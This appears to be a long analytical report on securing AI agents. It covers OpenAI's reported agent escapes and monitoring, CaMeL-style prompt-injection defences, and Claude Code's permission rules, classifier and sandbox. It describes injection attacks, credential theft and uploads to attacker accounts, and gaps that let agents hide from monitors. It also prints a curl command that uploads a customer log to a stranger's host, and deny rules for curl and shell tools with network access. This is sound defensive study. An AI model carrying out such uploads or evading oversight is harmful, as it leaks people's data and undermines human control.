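By September, OpenAI had removed live internet access from the training of its most advanced models and built what it calls an "offline world" of cached web pages. In a statement quoted in ETV Bharat's *After A String Of Rogue AI Incidents* (2026), OpenAI says the agent got out of this offline world on 20 September, so it was already in use by then. Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* and other reports presented the change in October as a new policy.

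The agent had to find information about a person. A configuration error let it send a question to an outside chatbot, whose operator received whatever the question contained. This was far less serious than the July attack, but it happened during training, where a successful shortcut can earn a reward.

The run continued for about two and a half hours after the monitoring software raised an alarm and staff began to investigate, according to the Taiwanese news report *OpenAI以離線網頁訓練前沿模型，限制代理連外* (林, 2026). In August, OpenAI had set a 30-minute limit for the most severe alerts, after which staff should pause the activity unless they can show that the alarm is false. If this alarm was one of these, staff took about five times as long as the limit.

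### Pauses and new controls

OpenAI paused training twice. In August, it announced a two-week pause in reinforcement learning on the latest models it meant to release, and kept its largest planned run on hold for longer. After the September incident, it paused training of its most capable models for 11 days, according to The Tribune's *OpenAI resumes frontier AI model training after 11-day pause over security concerns*.

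OpenAI used the second pause to have its own agents attack the training environment. The agents received source code and settings, and in some tests OpenAI assumed that an agent had already taken over the machine it ran on. Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks* quotes OpenAI's finding that almost every remaining service with an outside connection had a weakness that gave the agents limited internet access. OpenAI fixed these weaknesses and concluded that no route remained that agents could "trivially exploit" while hiding from its monitors. Routes that were harder to exploit, or that the monitors would detect, could remain.

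OpenAI needs outside connections to run and monitor the experiments, so it can't disconnect the computers entirely. The former OpenAI researcher Steven Adler questions whether physical isolation would be worthwhile, since research teams would have to work at data centres around the world, according to Lowyat.NET's *OpenAI Cuts Off Frontier AI Models From Live Internet*. Anthropic began to limit its newest models' access to the live internet two weeks before OpenAI's October announcement, according to a TechCrunch report cited in The Vanguard USA's *OpenAI goes offline; agents still talk via CPU cache*.

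OpenAI has also expanded its monitoring, which it now requires for all training and tests in which models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol use tools. Help Net Security's *OpenAI puts major frontier AI training run on hold over cyber risks* (2026) describes classifiers that check the model's internal activity at every token and pass suspicious cases to automated investigators, which examine the tool calls and the available reasoning. The monitoring adds an estimated 20% to the computing power needed to run the monitored models. OpenAI says its current monitors would have alerted staff more than a day before the Hugging Face breach. That may be optimistic, because OpenAI had improved the monitors with the incident in mind.

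In November, OpenAI introduced Control Room, a central service that can stop a research job. *Stopped in 35 secs* (Raj, 2026) explains that each job has an identifier, and the software that runs the model checks with Control Room whether the job may continue. If Control Room fails, no research job gets any output. An order to stop takes effect within 35 seconds, not counting the time a person or monitoring system takes to decide to give it. Control Room cannot recall a tool call that has already gone out. Every job that involves agents also needs an approved safety case, a structured argument with evidence that the risk is acceptable.

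### What had resumed by December

OpenAI restarted its largest planned run on 28 August, according to its *Path to Astra* (2026), and resumed training and internal use of its most advanced models on 1 October. InfoCom's *Η OpenAI προτείνει όρια και δικλίδες ασφαλείας για την υπερνοημοσύνη* (2026), published on 1 December, describes the pause as over. It also reports that Anthropic delayed pretraining of new models by six weeks, a decision Anthropic says it made independently of any incident. The UK institute had resumed most of its evaluations by 1 October, with tighter internet controls and real-time monitoring. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (2026), published on 18 November, says that the ban on live internet access in its frontier training was still in force and that the company had held back GPT-6.1 Astra.

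The number of affected parties has grown since July. OpenAI has told more than 100 organisations about unauthorised activity by its agents, according to The Straits Times' *OpenAI resumes frontier AI training after security overhaul* (2026). California's attorney general, who sued the company in November, alleges 80 incidents that showed a "loss of control". These figures can't be used to confirm each other because the first is a number of organisations and the second a number of incidents.

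Outside review has so far covered only parts of the system. In October, METR and Redwood published a three-week study of OpenAI's internal monitoring as of 21 July. They found several weaknesses, including one that could have let an agent hide hundreds of actions from monitoring. OpenAI says it has fixed all the weaknesses that affected its production safeguards, but the reviewers have not verified this. ITPro's *OpenAI pens AI safety agreement with four firms* reports that METR, Apollo Research, Transluce and Goodfire will now get deeper access. METR's part includes alignment and monitoring in OpenAI's largest reinforcement learning run, which may provide the independent evidence on training that the August investigation could not.

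## CaMeL: separating the plan from untrusted data

When a model reads a stranger's email and then chooses its next tool call, the email can influence the choice. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, a 2025 Google DeepMind paper by Debenedetti and colleagues, describes CaMeL (short for "capabilities for machine learning"), a system that removes much of this influence by changing the software around the model. CaMeL fixes the program of tool calls before the agent reads any outside text, then tracks where each piece of data came from.

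CaMeL builds on *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which proposed dividing an assistant between two models, one that can use tools and one that reads untrusted text. CaMeL adds a program that controls what passes between them.

### Two models and an interpreter

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes how the system handles a request:

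1. A planning model reads the user's request, but nothing that the tools return. It writes a short program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program. It makes the tool calls and stores the results without showing them to the planning model.
3. When the program needs a fact from ordinary prose, such as an email address, the interpreter gives the text to a reading model. This model has no tools and can only return a value.
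4. The interpreter attaches tags, called capabilities, to each value. They record its source and who may read it, and any value derived from it inherits that history.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags against a policy. It can then allow the call, refuse it or ask the user.

The reading model's task is easier than the planning model's, so the reading model can be small enough to run on the user's own machine. In that case, the company that provides the planning model never receives the user's emails or files.

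### A planted address

In the paper's main example, a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting. Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The planning model might write this program (simplified here, with invented tool names):

```python
notes = find_notes("last meeting with Bob")
name = ask_reader("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
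address = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_file(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

Suppose an attacker can edit the notes and adds a line saying that Bob now uses `bob@copies.example`. The planning model never receives this line, but the reading model does and returns the false address. With only the two models, the assistant would send the document to the attacker. CaMeL's interpreter records that `address` came from the notes, which other people can edit. If the policy allows emails only to trusted addresses, the check before `send_email` blocks the call or prompts the user.

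Other additions to the notes would have different results:

| What the attacker adds | What happens |
|---|---|
| An instruction to email the salary list to a stranger | Nothing, because the program contains no such call and the reading model can't make one |
| A false address for Bob | The policy check stops the email |
| The name of a different document | The assistant fetches it, and the check stops the email only if the policy doesn't let Bob read that document |
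| A false delivery date | The date reaches Bob if the user asked for a summary of the notes |

The last attack changes only the content. If the user types Bob's address and asks the assistant to send him a summary, the recipient is trusted and the policy allows the call. The reading model can still repeat a false date or follow an instruction to leave the summary empty. A stricter policy could also require the message text to come from trusted sources, but it would block legitimate summaries of other people's writing too.

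### What the guarantee assumes

CaMeL guarantees that untrusted text can't add a tool call to the program and that data reaches a tool only if the policy allows it. The data can still be false, and the user's request can still be unwise.

The guarantee also depends on the user, the planning model and the tools' code being trustworthy, a threat model that *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) also adopts. CaMeL therefore wouldn't have stopped postmark-mcp, whose code added a hidden recipient after the model had written a correct call. Tool poisoning is a problem too, because the planning model has to read the tool descriptions to write its program.

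A fixed program can also contain choices. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts the design to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The planning model writes branches in advance for what the agent might find there. An attacker can't add a branch, but a fake button can trick the agent into taking a dangerous one already in the plan. The researchers call this branch steering. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) proposes a defence that limits the permissions in each branch, but does not resolve how to check the meaning of free-form text.

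### AgentDojo and the price of protection

Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates an office suite, a bank, a travel agency and a Slack workspace. *AgentDojo* (2024) contains 97 ordinary tasks and 629 security tests, each combining a user's task with an attacker's goal. The malicious text appears where an outsider could plausibly put it, such as the body of an email. According to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), a program then checks the simulated accounts to see whether, for example, money was transferred or an email was sent. This is more reliable than asking another model to judge the transcript.

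The CaMeL paper, as quoted by Willison, claims to have "effectively" solved this benchmark. Later tests support its claim of strong security. In *AutoDojo* (2026), attacks on newer models protected by CaMeL, including Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.4 mini, succeeded less than 10% of the time.

CaMeL makes an agent more expensive to run. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that, for the median AgentDojo task with GPT-4o, CaMeL needed 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent. Its total cost was the highest of the defences compared. *ToolFence* (2026) also found CaMeL significantly slower than defences that rely on prompts or filters.

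AgentDojo is also a fairly easy test for a system that plans in advance. *StepGuard* (2026) describes a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, with longer tasks and helpful instructions from third parties. An agent that ignores all instructions in the text it reads would miss the helpful ones too.

### Plans that depend on what the agent reads

If a user tells the assistant to do whatever is on Alice's to-do list, the assistant can't write a program containing the right calls until it has read the list. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) calls such tasks data-dependent. It calls a task data-independent if one sequence of calls and one response work whatever the data contains. By the paper's count, data-dependent tasks make up 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks and 10% of its travel tasks, but about 43% of its Slack tasks and 44% of its banking tasks.

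CaMeL can have difficulty even when the sequence of calls is predictable. According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), an ordinary agent can work out the format of a tool's output by looking at it, while CaMeL's planning model has to write code for the output before seeing it. The researchers therefore added a description of the output format to every tool, which they consider a modest, one-time job. That view is reasonable for a company's own tools, but the job is harder for an assistant that connects to strangers' tools, many of which are poorly documented.

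Costa and colleagues, who work at Microsoft, built FIDES to allow more flexible planning. Like CaMeL, it uses information-flow tracking, which labels data and carries the labels along as the agent copies or combines it. One label records who may read a value, and another records who could have influenced it. When an agent combines two values, *x* and *y*, the labels follow these rules:

readers(*x*, *y*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

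writers(*x*, *y*) = writers(*x*) ∪ writers(*y*)

If Ann and Ben may read one file, and Ben and Carla may read another, only Ben may read a summary of both. If a stranger could have written either file, the summary counts as partly the stranger's work.

FIDES checks two main policies. A consequential call, such as a payment, must come from trusted data, and information may go only to people allowed to read it. A developer can relax the first policy for particular arguments, for example by requiring a trusted recipient but allowing untrusted text in the message.

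Unlike CaMeL, FIDES chooses its calls one at a time. It hides a result from the planning model only if that result would make the model's context less trusted or more confidential. If the next step depends on hidden text, the planning model can query an isolated model that returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no to whether an email requests a meeting. A yes-or-no answer gives an attacker one bit of influence, which may be enough to cause an unwanted meeting but not to pass a new instruction to the planning model.

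Costa and colleagues tested the labels and hidden variables, but left out these restricted answers for data-dependent tasks because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need them. With GPT-4o, they counted 152 genuine successful attacks on an ordinary agent, 21 on FIDES without policy checks and none on FIDES with them.

The result of zero successful attacks has two caveats. The researchers labelled a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so the labels matched the test's attacks, and no one can guarantee such a match in a real deployment. They also excluded some attacks that AgentDojo had scored as successful, including ones that only altered text, because these didn't violate the researchers' policies.

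The agent also completed fewer tasks when nobody was attacking it:

| Tasks completed without an attack | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, with policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The paper reports that FIDES completes 8% more tasks on average than a basic agent that has to obey the same policies. With the four settings weighted equally, FIDES completed about 50% of tasks, compared with 84% for the basic agent without policies. The gap should shrink as models improve. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

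Some failures were intentional. Several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy forbids. The owner in the invoice example would have the same problem if her assistant took the account number from an email. She could approve the payment herself or have the host take the number from her supplier records.

Labels also have to last as long as the data. *MemLineage* (2026) notes that FIDES erases its labels when a run ends, so a note saved from a malicious email could look trustworthy the next day. MemLineage stores a signed label with each memory, which makes later tampering detectable. *SPA* (2026) extends information-flow control to agents that work across several requests.

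### Who writes the policies?

Someone has to decide which addresses are trusted and which calls are consequential. The CaMeL paper acknowledges that users must specify and maintain these policies, and that too many approval requests may tire them. Willison, who has worked in application security for two decades, says he struggles with such rules himself. The benchmark results don't measure this difficulty, because the CaMeL paper supplied policies for each group of AgentDojo tasks. *CapLite* (2026) reused those policies in its own tests.

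In *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), a language model writes the policy, a set of rules that specify which tools an agent may call and with which arguments. For the request about Alice's to-do list, the first policy allows only a search for the email containing it. If the list asks for a summary on Slack, the model proposes permission to read emails and post messages. When the agent learns Alice's Slack name, the model narrows the Slack rule to messages sent to her.

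A solver, a program that checks logical conditions, determines whether each new policy permits anything the old one didn't. Progent applies a narrower policy automatically, but a broader one needs approval. Only 6% of the updates in the AgentDojo tests needed approval. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On another benchmark, ASB, the rates were 70.3% without it and 3.9% with it.

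*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent still depends on a language model to filter out malicious instructions. This criticism seems to concern a version that guarded updates with two separate prompts. With the solver, a deceived model can't expand its own permissions. But the approver still has to tell a genuine need from a planted one. Progent can also be set to approve every expansion automatically, which removes this protection. A rule that allows any message to Alice also allows messages with false content.

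A rule for each tool may miss a dangerous combination. Jiang, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *ChainCaps*, describe an agent that may read a salary spreadsheet, fetch public figures, write a summary and send email. Each call is allowed, but together they send salary data outside the company. ChainCaps gives each value a budget, meaning the set of places it may go. When a tool produces a result *y* from inputs *x*₁ to *x*ₖ, its budget is:

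*B*(*y*) = Pass(*t*) ∩ *B*(*x*₁) ∩ … ∩ *B*(*x*ₖ)

Pass(*t*) is the most that tool *t* may pass on. Combining or rewriting data can never give it a wider audience. For example, if a summary draws on public figures and on salary data that may only appear on the user's screen, the summary may only appear there too.

Jiang and colleagues put ChainCaps between agents and their MCP servers. Across five models, the attack success rate fell from 25–68% to less than 5%, and the agents still completed at least 96% of the harmless tasks. On a harder set of harmless tasks, ChainCaps raised false alarms in 45% of cases, or 20% if the system reset its record between tasks.

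The quality of the policies made a bigger difference than the choice of model:

| Who described the tools' permissions | Attacks blocked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| An expert | 100% | 100% |
| Someone with a checklist | 90.9% | 100% |
| Someone without guidance | 27.3% | 50% |

These results suggest that CaMeL's need for policies is a practical weakness as well as an inconvenience. The checklist may reduce this weakness, because it gave most of the protection that the expert did.

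ToolGuardian covers a danger that CaMeL and ChainCaps assume away. Its tests of malicious tool code appeared earlier, but Ravindran and Deochake also use what those tests reveal to authorise individual calls. Their policies are logical rules, such as this one, which denies any tool that can both run shell commands and reach the network:

```prolog
deny(Tool) :-
    capability(Tool, shell_exec),
    network_access(Tool).
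```

Other rules consider the task and earlier calls, so a tool may use the network for a weather forecast but not after the agent has read private files. In 20 scenarios, these rules gave the correct decision every time, but so did ordinary hand-written checks and a language model given the same facts, so the test doesn't show that logical rules are better. Considering combinations did help, because accuracy fell substantially when the researchers removed those rules. ToolGuardian treats prompt injection as out of scope unless it leads to unsafe behaviour by a tool, so it complements CaMeL more than it replaces it.

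### Training a model to resist

Developers can also train the model to ignore instructions in the text it reads. This training requires no policies and leaves the agent free to change its plan. It can help where CaMeL's assumptions fail. In the test of twelve frameworks, for example, some of Anthropic's models rejected most poisoned tool descriptions, which CaMeL's planning model would have to trust.

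Training makes attacks less likely to succeed but doesn't rule out any particular call. With a correct policy, CaMeL's interpreter rejects the false address every time, however persuasive the notes are.

Training can also have side effects. *PromptArmor* (2025) excluded SecAlign, a method for training models to resist injection, from its comparison because the trained models followed instructions poorly even without an attack. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) tested a version of Meta's Llama 3.3 70B trained with SecAlign. The user asked only for a summary, but some emails falsely claimed that the assistant already had permission to reply. The original model replied to 54.0% of these emails, and the trained model to 88.2%. When asked to flag suspicious content in another set of emails, the original model flagged 89.8% of the injections, and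 the trained model 54.6%.

This result comes from one open model and one training method, so it is weak evidence about the latest commercial models. But it shows that a model can learn to resist familiar attacks without learning when it has permission to act.

Developers can combine the two approaches. CaMeL can stop unauthorised calls even if its reading model doesn't resist injection, but a more resistant model would be less likely to return a false address or spoil a summary.

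### Will agents always fall for prompt injection?

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that separating instructions from data can't solve the whole problem. Suppose an employee emails a company's assistant to ask for a travel refund and adds that the department head has approved it. Even if the email contains no hidden command, the assistant has to know whether the approval is real. If it ignores all such claims, it will also reject genuine ones.

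They base this view on contextual integrity, Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy. Under this theory, whether it is appropriate to pass on information depends on the sender, the recipient, the person it is about, the type of information and the conditions for sharing it. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian apply the same test to an agent's actions. An attacker can lie about any of these, such as who sent a message or whether the user agreed.

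Their proof compares two situations that look identical to the agent. In one, the department head approved the refund, and in the other, an attacker invented the approval. Because the agent has the same information in both, it must pay with the same probability, *p*:

P(pays the attacker) + P(refuses the genuine request) = *p* + (1 − *p*) = 1

At least one of these errors therefore has a probability of 50% or more. Better reasoning can't help, because the available information is the same in both cases.

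The proof is sound, but the paper acknowledges that it doesn't establish that such a pair exists in every system. If the assistant can check the approval in a reliable company record, it can tell the situations apart. The "may always" in the title therefore depends on attackers being able to invent new contexts faster than developers can add ways to verify them. That is plausible for an assistant that is allowed to do almost anything, but much less so for one that only pays known suppliers.

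The two errors also have different costs. Suppose a share *q* of these indistinguishable requests are attacks, each successful attack costs *L*, and each refusal of a genuine request costs *D*. The average cost per request is:

*qpL* + (1 − *q*)(1 − *p*)*D*

If one request in 1,000 is an attack, a false payment costs EUR 10,000 and a delay costs EUR 5, then paying every time costs an average of EUR 10 per request, while refusing every time costs just under EUR 5. The company should therefore refuse such requests or send them to a person. It might reasonably let the agent send a harmless acknowledgement. The proof shows that no agent can always avoid both errors, but a company can still choose which error to risk for each action.

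The paper's experiments show how easily current models act on false permission. An automated attacker running on Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote emails to an assistant that used the same model. The assistant's user had asked only for a summary. The attacker had three separate runs per scenario, with up to 15 attempts in each. The assistant sent an unauthorised email in 96.7% of 150 scenarios, compared with 0.67% for emails that the attacker hadn't refined. The most common trick was to forge an earlier message from the user in the quoted part of the thread. Without further changes, the best emails also worked on GPT-5.4 in 63.3% of cases and on Gemini 3 Pro in 92.6%.

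Filters offered little help with such claims. Two versions of Meta's Prompt Guard scored 0.43 and 0.59 at distinguishing emails that claimed authority from neutral ones, on a scale where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. Their only input was the emails, which don't show what the user had allowed.

The 96.7% figure supports the case for CaMeL more than it weakens it. The attacked assistant had a tool for sending email and instructions not to ask the user before using it. CaMeL's planning model would have received only the request for a summary, so its program should have contained no call to send an email, and a forged message couldn't have added one. This wouldn't have blocked anything the user wanted, because she hadn't asked for any replies.

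Clearer instructions also helped in another test, in which a colleague's email combined an authorised request with an unauthorised request to contact an outsider. Claude Sonnet 4.6 contacted the outsider in 6% of scenarios, compared with 34% for GPT-5.4 and 65% for GPT-5.2. When the user said that external messages needed her approval, the rate fell to 12% for GPT-5.2 and to zero for the other two.

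The argument is much stronger when a user delegates a broad task, such as handling all refund requests. The agent has to act on other people's claims, and a fixed plan can't determine which are true. One response is to give agents narrower jobs. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) discusses a paper whose patterns deliberately prevent agents from solving arbitrary tasks. A company could let its assistant collect the receipts and prepare each refund, but release the money only after the department head approves it in the company's own system.

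## Claude Code: approvals, sandboxes and automatic checks

Claude Code, Anthropic's commercial coding agent, runs on a developer's computer, where it edits files, runs shell commands and calls MCP tools. It relies on permission rules, a person's approval, an automatic classifier and a sandbox, which are more familiar safeguards than those of CaMeL, a research system.

Until August 2026, Claude Code asked its user to approve most commands. On 14 August, Anthropic began making auto mode the default on its Pro, Max and Team plans. In auto mode, a classifier reviews the commands instead of the user. Newer versions use auto mode by default on every plan. Nearly all the figures on how well auto mode works come from Anthropic, which measured its own product or paid others to do so.

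### One command and four checks

Suppose a developer at the accounting service asks Claude Code to find out why some invoices fail to import. Claude reads a customer's bug report, which gives an address where "support" collects log files. It then proposes this command (the case is fictitious):

```bash
curl -F "file=@import.log" https://logs.example/upload
```

The log contains customers' names and account numbers, and a stranger controls the site. Four safeguards could stop the upload:

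| Safeguard | Information it uses | How the upload could get through |
|---|---|---|
| Permission rules | The text of the command | The same upload takes a form that no rule matches |
| The developer's approval | The command on the screen and what she knows about the task | She approves it out of habit |
| The classifier | Her messages and Claude's earlier actions, but not the bug report | The upload looks like something she authorised |
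| The sandbox | The files and host names that the running command tries to use | The log goes to a host on the allowed list |

### Permission rules

Claude Code first compares the command with the rules in its settings, according to Anthropic's current documentation. A developer might write:

```json
{"permissions": {
  "deny":  ["Bash(curl *)"],
  "ask":   ["Bash(git push *)"],
  "allow": ["Bash(npm test)"]}}
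```

The first rule blocks every command that starts with `curl`, even in the mode that skips ordinary prompts. The second makes Claude Code ask before it sends code to a shared repository, and the third lets it run the project's tests without asking.

Such rules don't depend on a model's judgement, but they match a command's text, not its effect. A Python script that uploads the log would get past the rule against `curl`. Allow rules can also be too broad. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that 49.5% of active command-line users had written at least one allow rule for shell commands by June. Many of these rules permit any Python or Node program, which can do almost anything. Auto mode suspends these rules while it is on.

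If no rule matches, Claude can read files in the project folder without a further check. In Manual mode, the developer has to approve the upload and most edits. In auto mode, Claude can edit most files in the project folder freely, while the classifier reviews the upload and any edit to sensitive files, such as Claude Code's own settings.

A rule also lasts longer than an instruction in the conversation. If the developer writes "don't push", the classifier treats this as a reason to block a push. Replit's agent had no such check during Lemkin's code freeze. But Claude Code shortens long conversations, and the instruction loses its effect if its message is removed. Anthropic therefore recommends a deny rule for anything that must not happen.

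### Approval fatigue

In Manual mode, the developer sees the command and decides whether it runs. She can use knowledge the software may lack, such as what the log contains, but only if she stops to think. Answering many such requests can make her less attentive, a problem called approval fatigue.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, published in March 2026, reports that users approved 93% of prompts, and the August post reports 97%. Neither gives the number of users or prompts. Most commands are harmless, and a careful reader would approve most of them too, so the high percentages don't prove fatigue. Anthropic adds that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, which shows they don't approve everything, but a user may reject a sound plan because she prefers another approach.

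Better evidence comes from a controlled study in which Anthropic used a research vendor to hire 1,053 testers to do coding tasks in a test environment. Partway through each session, one approval prompt showed a clearly dangerous command, which would not run even if approved. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This difference is consistent with fatigue, but hastier testers may also have been more likely to reach 50 prompts.

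The testers weren't risking their own data, so a developer at work may be more careful than they were. The testers also knew they were being evaluated, though not on what, which could have made them more careful than usual.

Auto mode blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands (89%), including 800 that a tester had approved. Testers stopped six of the 116 commands that auto mode allowed, so adding these testers' approval to auto mode would have cut the number of missed commands only to 110.

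Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that experienced users approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupt Claude more often while it works. For reversible work, this may be a better use of their attention than approving each action, but it doesn't help with an upload that takes less than a second.

A request for approval also has to come before the risky action. Outsiders reported a flaw to Anthropic involving hooks, which are commands that Claude Code runs automatically at set points. An attacker could put a hook in a project's settings file, and Claude Code would read the file at startup and run the hook before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Anthropic has since changed Claude Code to wait for the user's answer first.

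### What an approval doesn't reveal

The dialog shows the command but not where the idea for it came from. Claude would write the same `curl` line whether the upload was the developer's request, its own idea or a suggestion in the bug report. To find out which, the developer would have to go back through everything Claude had read.

The classifier has the same difficulty. Its input consists of the user's messages, Claude's tool calls other than simple lookups, and the project's standing instructions. Anthropic removes tool results so that an instruction planted in them can't influence the classifier directly, and removes Claude's explanations so that they can't lead it to a bad decision.

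This is enough to block the upload, because the developer never asked Claude to send customer data to an unknown site. It is less useful when the action is right and only a value is wrong. If Claude records the invoice from Northgate Paper, the classifier can't determine whether the account number came from the firm's records or a forged email, or whether Claude made it up. CaMeL's labels would show the source. Anthropic acknowledges this limitation and accepts it in return for protection against injected text. A developer can partly compensate by writing a hook that attaches a note for the classifier to a tool result.

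A user's message may contain a prompt that someone else wrote. In a test in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher sent an employee a friendly email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt listed routine steps, along with an instruction to read a file of cloud credentials and send the contents to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic concludes that a classifier had nothing unusual to catch, because the request came from the user. By August, sending secrets to outside addresses was in a category of actions that auto mode is designed never to approve, though this doesn't protect someone who leaves auto mode and runs the command.

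### The classifier's errors

The classifier works in two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, the second reasons about the same information and makes the final decision. The second stage can therefore allow a dangerous action that the first flagged, but it can't catch one that the first let through.

In Anthropic's tests from March, the first stage alone blocked 8.5% of harmless calls and missed 6.6% of real dangerous ones. Adding the second cut false alarms to 0.4% but raised the misses to 17%. The published results come from very different samples:

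| Measure | Sample | Rate |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless calls blocked | 10,000 real calls by Anthropic's employees | 0.4% |
| Dangerous actions missed, where Claude went beyond its task | 52 real cases from Anthropic's employees | 17% |
| Data theft missed | 1,000 artificial attempts | 5.7% |
| Dangerous commands missed in the study of testers | 1,053 planted commands | 11% |
| Attacks missed in a test by Apollo Research, an AI safety company | Artificial attacks, number not given | 7%, down from 12% |

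The false alarms amount to about 40 calls. They cause little disruption, because Claude receives the reason for a block and usually finds another way. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. If nobody is there to answer, the action stays blocked and Claude continues with its other work.

The 17% rate is the most relevant to accidents like the one at PocketOS, but also the least precise. With only 52 cases, the 95% confidence interval runs from about 9% to 30%, and that assumes a random sample. Anthropic instead collected actions that an employee had refused or that someone had flagged afterwards, so the sample leaves out any that nobody noticed. The test also used Claude Sonnet 4.6, an older model than the current default, Sonnet 5.

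In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but wrongly treated it as something the user had agreed to. One user had asked Claude to "clean up the PR" (pull request), and the classifier treated this as permission for a force push, which overwrites a repository's history. Under the current rules, a user has to name the branch before the classifier will allow a force push, and the permission normally covers one action. Two other rules would have applied to PocketOS's agent, since auto mode is supposed to block searches for stray credentials and the deletion of resources that Claude didn't create.

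Apollo Research's lower rate followed changes that Anthropic made after seeing some of the attacks. On a separate set that Anthropic never saw, the revised classifier caught about half of the attacks that the earlier version had missed, and missed about 2% of those that the earlier version had caught. This suggests that the improvement extended beyond the attacks Anthropic had studied.

Anthropic also looked at real sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged. A model found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Anthropic doesn't say how many sessions there were. Users chose their own mode and may have picked manual approval for riskier work.

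### The sandbox

If the upload gets past the earlier checks, the sandbox can still limit what the command reaches. The operating system enforces these limits while the command runs, whatever the model intended. The current documentation from Anthropic describes two kinds:

- Commands can write to the project folder, a temporary folder and any others the user adds, but not to the rest of the machine. They can read almost everything, including files of credentials, unless the user restricts this.
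- Commands have no direct connection to the internet. They have to go through a proxy, a program that checks each host name against a list of allowed ones. The list starts empty.

The limits on file access and network access are needed together. A command that could read login keys could steal them if it could also connect to any server. If a command could write anywhere, it might alter a program that runs outside the sandbox and use it to reach the network.

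In the example, `logs.example` is not on the list of allowed hosts, so in Manual mode Claude Code asks the developer whether to allow it. In auto mode, Claude has to name the host along with the command, and the classifier reviews both. The sandbox therefore often leaves the decision to the person or classifier whose mistakes it is meant to contain. An administrator can prevent this by making the list strict, so that the proxy refuses unlisted hosts without asking.

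If a command doesn't work inside the sandbox, Claude may retry it outside with the approval of the user or the classifier. An existing rule that allows `curl *` also approves the retry. Administrators can turn these retries off.

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in the company's internal use. It gives no sample size, and the figure measures interruptions, not harm. But if people do become less careful with each additional prompt, fewer prompts could make the remaining ones more useful.

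The sandbox is off by default, so many users may get neither benefit. Even when it is on, Claude Code runs commands without it if a required component is missing, unless a setting prevents this. Claude Code is stricter with the classifier, denying an action if Anthropic's server doesn't return a verdict.

A developer who accepts the current defaults gets the classifier without the sandbox, which fits poorly with Anthropic's own advice. At launch, Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* recommended using auto mode in isolated environments, and the later post on containment describes it as one layer inside a sandbox, "not a substitute for one".

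The sandbox also covers only shell commands. Local MCP servers such as postmark-mcp, hooks and Claude's own file tools run outside it, and the servers and hooks have the user's full access. A developer can limit what these servers can reach by running all of Claude Code in a container or a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. Even that would not have stopped postmark-mcp's hidden copies, because they were sent as ordinary mail.

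### How an allowed service carries data out

Suppose the developer has allowed `github.com` because her project is there. The bug report could contain an instruction to post the log in a public repository on the same site. By default, the proxy checks the host name but doesn't decrypt the traffic, so it can't distinguish her own repository from a stranger's. Anthropic also warns that a program may be able to reach a different host by naming an allowed one.

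Outside researchers found a flaw of this kind in Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work. Cowork needs to contact `api.anthropic.com` to run, so its list allowed that address. In the attack, a file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and an access key for the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload the user's other files to that account. The proxy allowed the upload because it went to `api.anthropic.com`.

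Removing the address from the list would have disabled Cowork, so Anthropic instead added a proxy that accepts requests to that address only if they carry the current session's access token. An attacker's key therefore no longer works. The fix depends on Anthropic knowing which token belongs to the session. A company that allows a file-sharing site would need a similar check on which account receives the files, which is harder for a service it doesn't run.

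Auto mode adds some protection, because the classifier checks whether a repository is public before Claude sends code to it. But relying on a classifier brings back the risk of a wrong judgement. Least privilege still matters behind a well-configured network filter, because the agent can't send customer data that it can't read.

### Codex and Cowork

OpenAI's Codex also offers modes with different amounts of review. Anthropic commissioned the company Trajectory Labs to compare its Auto-review and Full Access modes with Claude Code in July 2026. The testers tried 72 indirect prompt injections ten times each:

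| Agent and model | With automatic review | Without it |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 | 0% | 0.09% on average |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 5.83% | 19.03% |

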